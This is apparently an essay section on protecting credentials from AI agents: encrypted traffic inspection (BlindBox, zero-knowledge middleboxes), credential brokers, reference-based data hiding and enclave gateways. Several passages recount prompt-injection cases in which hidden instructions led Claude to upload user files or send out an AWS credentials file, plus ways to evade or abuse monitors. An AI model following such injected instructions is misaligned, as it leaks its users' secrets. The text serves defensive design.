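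A company that uses agents could easily go against this advice by accident. An agent's request might go through the company's web proxy, then a gateway, then another vendor's prompt filter, and each would decrypt it. Every extra decryption gives intruders another place to read the traffic and adds another TLS connection that someone could misconfigure. Decrypting only once removes those extra places, but an intruder who takes over the one remaining monitor can still read all the traffic.

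Netresec mostly agrees with the NSA but argues that investigators sometimes need a second proxy. If they suspect a computer has malware, they may want to examine its traffic with their own tools, but many inspection products don't let them export the decrypted data. Netresec makes a proxy for this purpose, so it has an interest in the question. Still, a temporary proxy for one suspicious machine would expose much less data than a permanent one for the whole company.

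The NSA's corrected version of December 2019 warns that inspection can also interfere with token binding, which ties an access token to a particular TLS session so that a thief can't use it elsewhere. A proxy replaces that session with two others, so the server may reject the token.

### How BlindBox matches encrypted text

Sherry, Lan and colleagues (2015), in *BlindBox*, described a monitor that finds keywords in encrypted traffic without being able to read the rest. The sender and receiver both run BlindBox's software. A third party that they trust, such as a security company, writes the list of keywords and signs it. With an agent as the sender and a model provider as the receiver, it works like this:

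1. The agent and the provider agree on a secret, as in ordinary TLS. From it they derive the usual key for encrypting traffic and a separate matching key, *k*. The monitor gets neither.
2. The monitor obtains each of its keywords encrypted with *k*.
3. The agent encrypts its message as usual. It also cuts the text into overlapping pieces of eight characters, called tokens, with one starting at every character. It encrypts each token for matching and sends the tokens along with the message.
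4. The monitor looks up each encrypted token among its encrypted keywords. If it finds a match, it can block the connection or alert someone.
5. If the message goes through, the provider decrypts it, makes the tokens again and compares them with the ones that the monitor forwarded. An agent therefore can't hide a password by sending tokens from a different text.

The second step is the hardest because the monitor has the keywords but must not learn *k*, and the agent has *k* but must not learn the keywords. An attacker who knew the keywords could more easily avoid them.

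BlindBox solves this with a garbled circuit, a scrambled program that gives the right output for one input without revealing how it works. The agent sends the monitor a garbled circuit that encrypts a keyword with *k*, and the monitor runs it to get the encrypted keyword. The monitor obtains the scrambled form of its keyword through oblivious transfer, a protocol that lets it pick the values it needs without showing the agent which ones it picked.

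The program rejects any keyword without the third party's signature, so the monitor can't search for words of its own choosing. The provider also makes a copy of the program, and the monitor checks that the two are identical in case the agent or the provider is dishonest. Every keyword needs a new program.

### Why identical tokens look different

If the same token always had the same encrypted form, the monitor could see which pieces of text repeat and guess common words from their frequency. BlindBox prevents this by including a counter:

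encrypted token = AES(AES(*k*, token), salt + *n*) mod 2^40

AES(key, value) is the value encrypted under the key with AES, a standard cipher. The salt is a starting number that the agent sends to the monitor, and *n* is the number of times this token has already appeared. The last part shortens the result to five bytes.

The monitor has AES(*k*, keyword) for each keyword on its list, so it can calculate the encrypted form each keyword will have when it next appears. It can't do this for any other text. When a keyword matches, the monitor adds one to that keyword's counter and calculates the next form.

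Suppose Tiger-winter-58 is on the list and build-7 is about to send the provider a configuration file with the line "DB_PASS=Tiger-winter-58". The password is longer than eight characters, so the monitor looks for two pieces of it, "Tiger-wi" and "inter-58". The line has 23 characters and produces 16 tokens:

| Token | Text | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | DB_PASS= | No match |
| 2 | B_PASS=T | No match |
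| 9 | Tiger-wi | Match |
| 10 | iger-win | No match |
| 16 | inter-58 | Match |

The other 11 tokens match neither piece. The two matches are seven characters apart, as they should be if the whole password is there. The monitor can tell that the password starts at the ninth character, but it can't read "DB_PASS=" or anything else in the file. If it only raises an alert and the agent sends the file again, the encrypted tokens will look different, but the monitor will still detect both pieces.

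The match has to be exact, so TIGER_WINTER_58 would get through unless the agent's software normalised the text before making the tokens.

### What someone who takes over BlindBox gets

An attacker who takes over a BlindBox monitor can switch off detection or block traffic, but can't read most of it. The attacker also can't rewrite a provider's reply to make the agent run a command, as a dishonest gateway can, because BlindBox keeps TLS's protection against tampering.

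But the monitor needs its keywords in readable form. This is acceptable for a list of known malware phrases, but if the list contains the company's passwords, the intruder gets them all. To store hashes instead, the company would have to change BlindBox so that the agent and the provider hash each piece of text before encrypting it.

The protection also disappears if the same attacker controls both the monitor and the keyword list. Sherry and colleagues warn against using BlindBox in that situation, because the attacker could sign any word and search the traffic for it. In many companies, one security team would probably run the monitor and write the rules. That team should at least keep the signing key on a different machine from the monitor.

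### Decrypting after a match

Exact keywords are enough for some jobs. Sherry and colleagues found that single keywords could handle all the rules in a public dataset for detecting leaked documents by marks hidden in the text. But in four sets of rules for detecting attacks on web traffic, single keywords covered at most 5% of the rules. Combining several keywords and their positions raised this to 29% to 67%. The remaining rules needed flexible patterns or small programs that examine the text itself.

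For these, BlindBox has a variant that lets the monitor decrypt a connection once a suspicious keyword appears in it. With each token, the agent sends a second value:

AES(AES(*k*, token), a different number) XOR the TLS key

XOR combines two values so that anyone who knows one of them can recover the other. A monitor with a matching keyword can calculate the first part, then recover the TLS key and read the connection. Without a match, the second value looks random.

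The variant is a poor fit for agents because one match exposes the whole connection. An agent may use the same connection for hours, and a monitor that has recorded the encrypted traffic can decrypt the earlier messages too. An attacker who controls the monitor could cause a match by putting one of the monitor's keywords on a web page the agent is likely to read. The agent would add the page to its conversation and send it to the provider, and the attacker could then decrypt everything else on the connection.

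### BlindBox's speed and set-up time

Once a connection is open, BlindBox matches traffic quickly. Sherry and colleagues measured 166 megabits per second in their main test, although their introduction gives up to 186 per processor core. Snort, a widely used tool that inspects unencrypted traffic, reached 85 on the same data. The comparison somewhat favors BlindBox, which only did exact matching and used faster software for receiving data.

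At the measured speeds, the agent would take about 0.6 milliseconds to encrypt a 10,000-character message, including its tokens, and the monitor would take about 0.2 milliseconds to check it against 3,000 rules. The tokens would add about 50 kilobytes to a 10-kilobyte message, but this overhead is small for an agent that waits several seconds for each reply.

The garbled circuits make connections much slower to open. An ordinary TLS connection took 0.07 seconds to open, while BlindBox took 0.65 seconds with 10 keywords, 1.6 with 100, 9.5 with 1,000, and 97 with about 10,000. Each circuit is also 599 kilobytes, so for 1,000 keywords the agent and the provider would each send the monitor about 600 megabytes.

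Long secrets make this worse. A 40-character API key has five pieces, so 1,000 such keys would need 5,000 circuits and take about 48 seconds. The company could avoid most of this by looking for only one random piece of each key, since that piece is very unlikely to appear elsewhere by chance.

A ten-second wait at the start of each connection could be tolerable for an agent that keeps one connection to its provider open all day, but an agent that visits 50 websites would have to wait 50 times. Researchers are still working on this step, and *PrivBox* (Wu, Ning and colleagues, 2025) proposes a new way to generate the encrypted rules.

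### Proving that a message obeys the rules

A middlebox is any device that inspects or changes traffic on its way through a network. A zero-knowledge proof convinces someone that a statement is true without revealing the information behind it. *Zero-Knowledge Middleboxes* (Grubbs, Arun and colleagues, 2022) proposes that the sender use such a proof to show that an encrypted message follows the network's policy.

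Their main example is a network that blocks certain websites. Before a program can visit a site, it has to look up the site's address, and many programs now encrypt these lookups. For an agent on such a network, the method works like this:

1. The agent's software downloads the list of blocked sites from the monitor.
2. The agent opens an ordinary TLS connection to the lookup service. The monitor keeps a copy of the opening messages, in which the two ends agree on a key.
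3. The agent encrypts its request and creates a proof that the request, decrypted with the key from those opening messages, names a site that isn't on the list.
4. The monitor checks the proof and forwards the request.

The proof has to mention the opening messages so that it is tied to the agreed key. In TLS 1.3, the current version, a dishonest sender may be able to find a second key that decrypts the same message to a different text. The agent could then request a blocked site and use the second key to prove something about a harmless one.

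The sender takes about 14 seconds to create the proof for a new connection and 3 to 8 seconds for each later message, while the monitor can check a proof in 2 to 5 milliseconds. The sender also has to store hundreds of megabytes of data to make proofs. If a dishonest monitor supplied this data, senders might be able to forge proofs, but the monitor still couldn't read their traffic.

This technique could enforce the rule in David and colleagues' running example that an agent may use only the GET and HEAD methods. Grubbs and colleagues tested a policy that examines the first line of a web request, which also contains the method. An agent could therefore prove that it used GET without showing a proxy the passwords in the rest of the request. But each proof would take 3 to 8 seconds, so proving the 10,000 requests that the client permits would take 8 to 22 hours.

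### Faster proofs, with tighter limits

*Zombie*, a 2024 system by Zhang, DeStefano and colleagues, makes the proofs much faster. TLS 1.3 can encrypt a message by combining it with a pad, a string of random-looking data. The pad doesn't depend on the message, so the sender can create it in advance and do the slowest part of the proof while idle. This reduces the delay for a website lookup to under 300 milliseconds.

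Zombie can also remove the delay by letting the message through at once and checking the proof afterwards. This may be fine for a school that wants to know who visits blocked sites, but a monitor meant to stop password theft would catch it only after the password had been sent.

The monitor can handle only about 380 small packets, or less than one megabit, per second, even when it checks proofs in batches. Searching for patterns, such as the format of an identity number, adds 1 to 2 milliseconds per character. A 10,000-character message would take 10 to 20 seconds, and an agent's 50th request, with 500,000 characters, would take 8 to 17 minutes. The monitor can't skip the part of the conversation it has already checked, because it can't identify which part is new.

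Zhang and colleagues built Zombie for policies that are public and apply to each packet separately. A company couldn't use its list of passwords as the policy, because every agent would receive the list. Zombie would also miss a secret split between two packets.

### Which checks work for agents

These methods work for rules about exact text and simple structure. A monitor could search for a known API key, block certain websites or restrict the type of request. It could also use BlindBox to find hidden marks the company puts in its confidential documents.

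Systems that inspect traffic without reading it can't normally judge what a message means. An agent could reveal the password Tiger-winter-58 by describing it as a large striped cat, the coldest season and the number after 57, with hyphens between them. No eight-character piece of the password appears in that description. A language model might detect the leak, but it would need the unencrypted text. Fully homomorphic encryption can in principle run any program on encrypted data, but Sherry and colleagues estimated in 2015 that it was at least 100 million times slower than ordinary computing. Proofs are also far too slow for a calculation as large as running a language model, since even the encryption in TLS accounts for most of the work in a website lookup.

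BlindBox also assumes that either the sender or the receiver is honest. If both cheat, they can encrypt the secret a second time, and the monitor will find nothing. Sherry and colleagues point out that commercial leak-detection tools assume the same. These tools mainly target accidental leaks, since a deliberate one requires control of the sender's computer. But a coding agent often has that control. If a malicious web page tricks it into encoding a password before sending it, the tokens will still match the message, and BlindBox will miss the password just as a hashed list would.

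### Who has to change their software

| Method | Agent's software | Provider or website | What someone who takes over the monitor can read |
|---|---|---|---|
| Decrypting proxy | Must trust the proxy's certificates | No change | All the traffic |
| BlindBox | Must change | Must change | The keywords, and where they appear |
| BlindBox with decryption | Must change | Must change | The keywords, and every connection with a match |
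| Zero-knowledge middlebox | Must change | No change | The policy, and whether each message follows it |

The monitor needs special software in every case. It can also still see where messages go, when, and roughly how long they are.

Changing every website is unrealistic. In January 2022, almost four years after TLS 1.3 was completed, only 51% of servers supported it, while half of Chrome's users had a version less than a month old, according to Grubbs and colleagues. They therefore designed a method that only the sender and the monitor have to adopt.

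The obstacle may be smaller for traffic between agents and model providers, because a few providers handle much of it and some of them also make coding agents. Anthropic, for example, could add BlindBox to both Claude Code and its own servers, but would do so only if it wanted its customers' employers to use BlindBox. Traffic to websites and outside tools would still need a different solution.

Neither BlindBox nor a zero-knowledge middlebox can replace a gateway like LiteLLM, because they can only check messages, not add the provider's key to them. If a company used one of them instead, every agent would need its own copy of a provider key.

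## Credential brokers: keeping secrets from agents by holding them in one place

A credential broker keeps the real credentials and adds them to requests it approves, so an agent can use a service without holding a key it could leak. LiteLLM's proxy does this with provider keys, and a broker can do the same for GitHub tokens, server logins and many other credentials. The broker can't store only hashes of the credentials, because it has to send the originals to the services. Someone who takes over the broker can therefore use every credential in it, and can usually copy them too.

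### How a request gets its credential

Suppose build-7 has finished a code change and needs to propose it on GitHub:

1. The agent tells the broker which service it wants, or sends an ordinary web request with a placeholder where the GitHub token should be.
2. The broker identifies the agent that is asking.
3. It checks whether its policy lets build-7 use this token for this request.
4. If so, it puts in the real token and sends the request to GitHub.
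5. It removes any copy of the token from GitHub's reply and passes the rest to build-7.

Docker Sandboxes runs coding agents in isolated environments. According to Docker's *Manage credentials*, the real credential normally stays in the keychain of the developer's computer, and the agent sees only a placeholder such as "proxy-managed". A proxy outside the isolated environment writes the credential into each request. The proxy must terminate TLS to do this, so it can also read the rest of the request.

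For some secrets, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real secret only in approved headers of requests to approved domains. If a malicious web page tricks build-7 into sending the placeholder to notes.example, the attacker gets a useless string. The proxy never replaces placeholders in the body of a request. Otherwise, an attacker could tell the agent to post the placeholder in a public GitHub comment, and the proxy would publish the real token.

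The last step matters because a service may repeat the request's headers in an error message. Docker's proxy searches replies for these secrets in their original form and in three common encodings, including base64. It can still miss a secret that the service splits between two fields.

### CapSeal: permission for one narrow action

*CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) describes a stricter broker. When the agent opens a session, the broker uses the operating system to identify the calling program, so one program can't pose as another. The agent then requests permission for a specific action, such as sending POST requests to one address on api.example.com with a named key. The broker's policy can grant the request, refuse it, or require further approval.

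If the policy grants access, the broker gives the agent a handle, which is an identifier that works only in that session, expires, and can be used a limited number of times. Each use needs a new sequence number, a one-time value and a timestamp, so nobody can reuse a recorded request. The broker checks the request's method, address, size, headers and format before it uses the key. It then adds an entry to a log where later changes can be detected.

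CapSeal also rejects any authorization header that the agent supplies. *How we contain Claude across products* describes an attack on Anthropic's Cowork agent that shows why this matters. A malicious file contained hidden instructions and the attacker's own Anthropic key, and Claude used that key to upload the user's files to the attacker's account. The proxy, which let the agent contact only approved domains, allowed the upload because Anthropic's own domain was on the list. Anthropic fixed this by accepting only requests that carried the session's own token.

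For SSH, the usual protocol for logging in to servers, CapSeal's broker runs the command itself. In one example, the agent may use only one account on one server, may add up to three arguments to an approved command, and receives at most 2,048 bytes of output. The broker also checks the server's identity against a stored key.

CapSeal's prototype covers only web requests and SSH. Databases usually have their own protocols, so the broker would need another component to run queries using a database password like Tiger-winter-58.

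### What the CapSeal tests measured

Jin and colleagues compared CapSeal with two systems that give the agent its credentials directly. When a prompt told the agent to reveal a web service's key, both systems leaked it every time. CapSeal never did, since an agent behind it has no key to reveal.

The tests provide much less evidence about misuse. The researchers also prompted agents to use credentials at unauthorised addresses or for unauthorised commands, but these attempts failed in all three systems, including the two without a broker, so the result can't show that CapSeal's policy checks made a difference. SSH keys didn't leak from any of the systems either.

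The broker added about 0.15 milliseconds to a web request and 0.2 milliseconds to an SSH command. The tests used local servers and no language model, but the delay would be negligible for an agent that waits seconds for each reply.

CapSeal assumes that no attacker has administrator access to the computer it runs on. An attacker with that access could read the broker's memory or replace its program. Jin and colleagues acknowledge that the broker "remains a high-value target", and their design does not cover isolating customers who share a broker.

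### Testing a commercial vault from the inside

In September 2026, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues at Corvic AI tested their company's own product, Corvic Security Vault. They ran code in the environment where an agent's programs would run and tried to find the credentials (*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, 2026). They used their own account and tested no other product.

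There were two experiments, each with one connector, Corvic's name for a stored link to an outside service. One connector was for GitHub and the other for FRED, an economic data service. The researchers wrote down the secure outcome for each of 16 probes in advance:

| What the probes checked | Probes | Secure outcome |
|---|---|---|
| The vault adds the credential only for the right service | 5 | 5 |
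| No credential in environment variables | 2 | 2 |
| No credential in files | 2 | 2 |
| No credential sent to other services | 2 | 2 |
| No credential visible to the calling code | 2 | 2 |
| No access to the cloud platform's own credentials | 2 | 2 |
| An authorised request works | 1 | 1 |

The most useful probes sent requests to echo services, websites that return whatever they receive. None of the replies contained a credential. A request to GitHub succeeded even though the code that made it had no token, so the vault must have added one.

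The FRED connector never worked because it was set to put the key in a header, but FRED expects it in the web address. The researchers scored this separately, as a configuration fault rather than a security failure. But it weakens the FRED results, because a vault that never attached the key to anything would also have passed the leak probes. The GitHub experiment doesn't have this problem.

Kenney and colleagues ran all their probes from the agent's side. They did not verify how the vault encrypts its credentials, separates its customers or restricts its administrators, and these determine what an intruder in the vault could take. They also didn't test redirects, in which an approved service sends the request on to another address. The study is therefore reasonable evidence that an agent can work without seeing its credentials, but it provides no evidence about how hard the vault is to break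 into.

### Replacing sensitive data with references

A broker for logins doesn't protect secrets that the agent reads while working, such as a customer record or a password in a configuration file. *SecureClaw*, a system from June 2026, also keeps these secrets from the agent.

In the example that Ma and Schmid (2026), in *SecureClaw*, use, an agent has to send an invoice to someone for approval:

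1. A trusted gateway fetches the invoice, puts it in a trusted store, and gives the agent a reference, here called INV_42. It adds a short summary: vendor A, $4,200, due Friday.
2. The agent uses the summary to decide what to do and proposes sending INV_42 to the approver.
3. A policy engine approves that exact request, including the recipient.
4. A separate program, the executor, checks that the request still matches the approval. Only then does it fetch the real invoice and send it.

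If the agent changes the recipient after the approval, the executor refuses. The agent can pass the reference INV_42 to other agents or save it in memory, but can't use it to retrieve the invoice. The reference expires, and the store records who may use it, in which session, and where the executor may send the contents.

This also reduces what other monitors see. The conversation the agent keeps resending contains INV_42 instead of the invoice, so a dishonest router between the agent and the model provider would learn only what was in the summary.

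### Why the reference is neither a hash nor an encrypted copy

The formula for a reference does use a keyed hash:

reference = HMAC(secret key, one-time value, session, object)

HMAC is a standard way to compute keyed hashes. The inputs identify where and when the gateway stored the object, not its contents, so storing the same identity number twice produces two unrelated references.

A thief who has only a reference must go through the store to get the number. With the right key, the thief could decrypt an encrypted copy of the number or recover it from its hash by guessing, but a reference can't be decrypted or used to check guesses.

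Guessing a reference is also practically impossible. If 1,000 references of 128 bits are in use, a million random guesses have about a 3 in 10^30 chance of matching one.

### What the summary reveals

The summary is much less secure than the reference. Fixed rules create it, without a language model. The rules keep up to eight items from each list and the first 512 characters of each text field, and replace email addresses, account numbers and web addresses with tokens.

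To measure what gets through, Ma and Schmid made 122 pairs of documents that differed in one sensitive place and compared the summaries. The summaries differed for 35 pairs, or 28.7%. Swapping one email address or bank account number for another never changed the summary. Changing a subject line, a person's name in a transaction, or ordinary text within the first 512 characters always changed it.

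The 28.7% depends on which pairs the researchers chose, so it isn't a general leak rate. The pattern is more informative, because it suggests that if build-7 read a short configuration file as text, the summary would probably include the password Tiger-winter-58 in full. For passwords, a company should therefore turn off the summary and give the agent only the reference.

### How SecureClaw performed

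Ma and Schmid tested SecureClaw on three public collections of attacks, mainly with GPT-4o mini, a small and fairly old model:

| Test | Attacked tasks | No defence | SecureClaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: attack succeeded | 629 | 31% | 0.6% |
| Agent Security Bench: attack succeeded | 2,000 | 92% | 0% |
| AgentLeak: data leaked | 496 | 94% | 3.2% |

They repeated the Agent Security Bench test with four other models, including GPT-5.6 Luna, and again no attack succeeded. On AgentDojo, the share of ordinary tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 70% to 61%.

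Of the 16 leaks in AgentLeak, 15 were in the agent's final answer and one was in a message between agents. To find out which part of the system prevented other leaks, the researchers switched parts off in 24 attacked tasks. Without references, five tasks leaked data in messages between agents and two leaked it through shared memory. With references but without the approval checks, no task leaked data through either channel. The sample is small, but it suggests that the references kept data out of these internal channels.

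The protection depends on the gateway recognising which data is sensitive. In a separate test, Ma and Schmid made it miss sensitive fields at random. Protected values leaked in 3.6% of attacked tasks when it missed 1% of the fields, and in 13% when it missed 10%. An automatic detector found 99.2% of the sensitive fields, but it missed at least one in 117 of 996 tasks. A more cautious method, which marked fields as sensitive based on the structure of the data, leaked nothing in any of the 996 tasks, and the agent still completed 86% of them. Marking too much data as sensitive therefore seems much safer than marking too little.

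Ma and Schmid state that these guarantees require an honest gateway, store, policy engine and executor. Whoever controls the gateway can read the protected data as it arrives, and whoever controls the store can read everything in it. A gateway that only passed the invoice along would have held it for a second or two, but the store has to keep it until the agent finishes its task.

### When does a broker lose fewer credentials?

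Suppose a company has forty agents, and each holds three credentials that no other agent has. Each agent has a 2% chance of being compromised in a given year, independently of the others. On average, the company loses this many credentials a year:

40 × 3 × 0.02 = 2.4

If a broker holds all 120 credentials instead, and has a yearly chance *q* of being compromised, the average loss is 120 × *q* credentials a year. The average losses with and without a broker are equal when *q* is 2%. The number of agents doesn't change this break-even point, because it multiplies both averages. A broker loses fewer credentials on average only if it is harder to break into than a single agent.

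The averages conceal very different risks:

| | Agents hold the credentials | One broker, 2% risk |
|---|---|---|
| Average yearly loss | 2.4 | 2.4 |
| Chance of losing none | 45% | 98% |
| Chance of losing more than nine | 0.8% | 2% |
| Loss from a single break-in | 3 | 120 |

With the broker, the company will probably go decades without losing a credential and then lose all 120 at once. Many companies would prefer the frequent small losses, since they can replace three credentials in an afternoon but might have to stop work to replace 120.

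The calculation changes if all forty agents use the same three credentials. Compromising any one agent is then enough to get them all, and the chance that this happens at least once is:

1 − 0.98^40 ≈ 55%

A broker now breaks even at a 55% chance of compromise, and a badly run broker should still have a lower chance than that. The argument for a broker gets stronger as more agents share a credential.

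Many companies will fall between these two cases. If all the agents share two credentials and each also has one of its own, the broker holds 42 credentials and breaks even at about 4.5%. This is much closer to 2% than to 55%, because 40 of the 42 are unshared.

Assuming that agents are compromised independently favours brokers when the agents share credentials. The malicious LiteLLM release in March could have reached every machine that installed it. If all forty agents were always compromised together, with a 2% chance each year, the break-even point for shared credentials would drop from 55% to 2%. For unshared credentials it would stay at 2%, but the company could then lose all 120 credentials at once even without a broker.

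The calculation also counts only stolen credentials. An attacker who controls an agent can still use its three credentials through the broker until someone notices, but can't keep them for later.

### The case for centralising

The best argument for a broker is that agents are easy to trick. In an internal security exercise in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic emailed a colleague and persuaded them to paste a prompt into Claude Code. Among routine set-up steps, the prompt included instructions to read the colleague's AWS credentials file and send the contents to an outside address. According to Anthropic, Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. A broker doesn't follow instructions in emails or web pages, and if one had held the credentials, the file would have contained no usable secrets.

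Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* explains why the company moved its hosted agents' tokens out of the environment where Claude's code runs. For outside tools, a proxy fetches the credential from a vault and makes the call. Anthropic considered narrowing the tokens' permissions instead, but that would have meant guessing what Claude can't do with them, and the guess could become wrong as models improve.

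A broker also makes credentials easier to replace. A company that discovers a leaked GitHub token can change it once instead of on forty machines. In Docker's product, running local environments pick up new values for most stored secrets without a restart. A company might also afford better protection for one broker than for forty agents, which would bring the broker's risk below the break-even point.

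### The objection: one break-in, everyone's tokens

Hackers do break into services that hold other people's tokens. In August 2025, they stole tokens from Salesloft, whose AI chatbot connects to its customers' other software. Krebs on Security's *The Ongoing Fallout from a Breach at AI Chatbot Maker Salesloft* (2025) reports that these included valid tokens for hundreds of online services, among them Slack, Google Workspace, Microsoft Azure and OpenAI. The hackers took data from many companies' Salesforce accounts for at least ten days and searched it for more credentials.

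In October 2026, attackers got into OpenCode Console, essentially a broker for provider keys that lets teams share AI models without giving each member the keys. Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenCode Breach Could Affect OpenAI, Anthropic and Google* reports that the attack affected 1.4% of Console users, all of whom had linked outside providers. The attackers had entered an old system that OpenCode was shutting down. Some users reported unauthorised charges from hundreds of dollars to more than $1,000, according to Global Security Mag's *OpenCode breach exposes AI credentials, triggers unauthorized charges* (2026).

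A company can also depend on a broker it didn't choose. Hyperagent, an agent platform, connected to outside services through another company, Composio. Hyperagent's *Composio Security Incident* says that an intrusion at Composio in May 2026 affected the GitHub tokens of a small number of Hyperagent's customers. Hyperagent's own systems were not involved.

These cases show that a company using an outside broker shares the risk with that broker's other customers. An attacker who would never bother with forty agents at one small company may put a lot of effort into attacking a service with thousands of customers. The cases can't be used to estimate how often brokers fail, because nobody has counted the brokers that didn't fail.

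### Short-lived and narrow tokens

A company can make a break-in less damaging by having the broker issue tokens that expire soon. A one-hour token stolen at a random moment will work for another 30 minutes on average.

Even a five-minute token may last too long. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke* (2026) describes an attack that Microsoft disclosed in November. An attacker's AI agent searched GitHub, found a leaked secret, and used it to log in to a company's cloud account. Five minutes after starting the search, it was taking data from the company's store of keys. An attacker this fast can use a five-minute token before it expires, though the expiry does prevent the thief from coming back the next day.

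A broker can also make a stolen token useless to anyone but the agent it was meant for. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) describes a design in which each agent has its own cryptographic identity. When one agent gives part of its task to another, the broker issues a new short-lived token that works only for the receiving agent and grants only the permissions needed for that part. If the company cancels a token, the broker also cancels all the tokens derived from it.

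These measures mostly limit theft from agents and logs. An attacker who controls the broker can issue new tokens for as long as the break-in lasts. A broker also often stores a long-lived credential that it uses to get the short-lived ones, and the company has to replace that credential after a break-in.

Narrow permissions still help if the broker is compromised, because the outside service enforces them. Kenney and colleagues used their own judgement to rate eight threats before and after adding their vault, on a scale where 25 is worst. The score for sending credentials to the wrong service fell from 20 to 4, but the score for connectors with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15. A GitHub token that can delete every repository is almost as dangerous in a vault as outside one, since the agent can still use it through the vault.

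A broad token can also give an attacker access to other secrets. In April 2026, an attacker used a token stolen from Context.ai, an AI tool, to take over the Google account of an employee at the hosting company Vercel. Help Net Security's *Vercel breached via compromised third-party AI tool* (2026) reports that the attacker then read some of the settings Vercel stored for its customers. A token limited to a single calendar would probably not have given the attacker a way to reach those settings.

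An agent can still use a valid, narrow token on the wrong target. *AI Identity* (2026) points out that OAuth 2.1, a common standard for such tokens, checks whether a token is valid and has the right permissions, but not whether a malicious web page manipulated the agent into making the request. SecureClaw has a similar gap. In the four AgentDojo attacks that succeeded against it, the agent took a permitted kind of action on the wrong person or object.

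### One broker per team

Instead of one broker for forty agents, the company could have eight brokers for eight teams of five. Each would hold 15 credentials. If each broker has a 2% chance of compromise a year, the company still loses an average of 2.4 credentials a year, but a single break-in exposes 15 credentials instead of 120. The chance of at least one break-in a year rises from 2% to about 15%.

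Eight brokers are also more work to maintain. If they get less attention and each one's risk doubles to 4%, the average loss also doubles, to 4.8. And if all eight run the same software, one unpatched flaw might let an attacker into all of them, and splitting them would then achieve little.

*Caging the Agents* (2026), a security design for healthcare, puts a small broker beside each group of agent programs. Each broker limits the number, size and destinations of requests. An attacker who takes over an agent can send requests through its broker but can't get the keys the broker holds.

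However, splitting a broker helps only if the resulting brokers hold different credentials. If forty brokers all held the same three company-wide keys, the chance of losing those keys would be 55% each year, the same as if forty agents held them. A company should therefore get separate keys for each team before it splits the broker.

### Keys that can sign but not leave

The broker can avoid holding a copyable key if the outside service accepts digital signatures. The service sends a random value, a hardware chip signs it with a private key that never leaves the chip, and the service checks the signature with the matching public key. An intruder can request signatures from the chip while in control of the broker but can't copy the key, so the company may not need to replace it afterwards.

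Docker offers something similar for SSH, although the key may be in ordinary software on the developer's computer instead of a chip. Programs in the isolated environment can request signatures but can't read the key. Jin and colleagues deliberately avoided this approach in CapSeal. They argue that an agent that can freely request signatures still has a powerful credential, and that its use is hard to limit. A broker could instead keep the key in a chip and check each action before requesting a signature.

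*Agent Authenticator* (2026) proposes combining these protections. Each agent would have hardware-held keys that work only for particular services, and individual actions could require a person's approval. The system is designed to work with existing login standards, so companies could adopt it gradually. But services that accept only an ordinary API key would have to change, because anyone with a copy of such a key can use it.

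A chip also can't check whether the broker's request for a signature is legitimate. An attacker who replaces the broker's program can make the chip sign anything the key permits. Jin and colleagues suggest running the broker in an attested enclave, a hardware-isolated program that can prove to others which code it runs. Airlock also relies on this kind of hardware.

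## Monitors inside attested hardware: AEGIS and Airlock

Two systems from 2026 use attested enclaves for agent traffic. AEGIS prevents a gateway's operator from reading conversations, while Airlock prevents an agent from tampering with the monitor that restricts it.

### How an enclave proves which code it runs

An enclave depends on three features of the hardware:

- Isolation keeps the enclave's memory out of reach of everything else on the machine, including the operating system and its administrator. Some processors can isolate a whole virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. This is called a confidential virtual machine.
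- Measurement means that the platform computes a hash of the exact program it loads.
- Attestation means that the platform signs a document containing the measurement. Anyone can trace the signature back to the company that made the platform.

A client that has the expected measurement can compare it with the one in the document. But a dishonest operator could send an old document, or send one from a real enclave while routing the traffic to an ordinary program. To prevent this, the client sends a random value, and the enclave includes it in the document along with a hash of its TLS certificate. The random value shows that the document is new, and the hash lets the client check that its encrypted connection ends inside the enclave.

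### One request through AEGIS

Xie and colleagues built AEGIS on Amazon's Nitro Enclaves and put only a small relay in the enclave. Logins, account selection, key storage and billing stay on the host, the ordinary part of the machine, which the operator controls.

Before anyone uses the gateway, the operator publishes the relay's source code and records the release in a public append-only log. A customer, or the customer's coding agent, reviews the code, builds it and saves the resulting measurement. The log makes it hard for the operator to give one customer a secret version.

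Suppose build-7 then sends the model a conversation that contains the password Tiger-winter-58:

1. The request goes to a sidecar, a small program on the developer's machine. The sidecar asks the enclave for an attestation.
2. The sidecar checks the signature, the measurement, the random value and the certificate, and makes sure that debugging is off. If any check fails, it sends nothing.
3. The sidecar sends the conversation and the developer's gateway key over the connection that ends in the enclave.
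4. The enclave passes the gateway key to the host. The host checks it, chooses an account, and returns the provider's name and the provider key.
5. The enclave looks up the provider's address in a list inside its own program. The host can't add an address, so it can't redirect the conversation to its own server.
6. The enclave replaces the gateway key with the provider key and sends the conversation on unchanged.
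7. It returns the provider's reply byte for byte, then tells the host how many tokens to bill.

The sidecar verifies the enclave once per session. Each connection carries only part of the information:

| Connection | What it carries | What it never carries |
|---|---|---|
| Sidecar to enclave | The conversation and gateway key, after verification | The conversation before verification |
| Enclave to host, to get an account | The gateway key; labels for the model, platform and session; accounts that failed | The conversation; any destination |
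| Host to enclave | Names of the provider, policy and account; a billing label; the provider key | A network address; instructions to change the conversation |
| Enclave to provider | The unchanged conversation; the provider key; approved headers | The gateway key; a destination chosen by the host |
| Enclave to host, for billing | Token counts, status and delay | Prompts, replies or tool calls |

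As the third row shows, the host still stores the provider keys, so a flaw like LiteLLM's SQL injection would expose them as before, although the thief couldn't read the conversations. Xie and colleagues suggest encrypting the provider keys under a key that only the enclave holds, but their prototype doesn't do this.

### What the AEGIS tests measured

Xie and colleagues tried four attacks that Liu and colleagues had described: rewriting a tool call, swapping a software package for one with a similar name, rewriting only under certain conditions, and copying secrets. All four worked on an ordinary gateway and failed against AEGIS, as expected from its design, because the host has access only to encrypted text. The tests are good evidence that the prototype works as intended, but they weren't a search for unknown flaws.

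The relay added a median of 5.7 milliseconds to a small request. An ordinary program doing the same work added 3.7 milliseconds, so the enclave and the sidecar accounted for about 2 milliseconds. The delay rose to 52 milliseconds for a one-megabyte request and 183 for four megabytes. Even the larger delays are short compared with the second or so that a model takes to answer.

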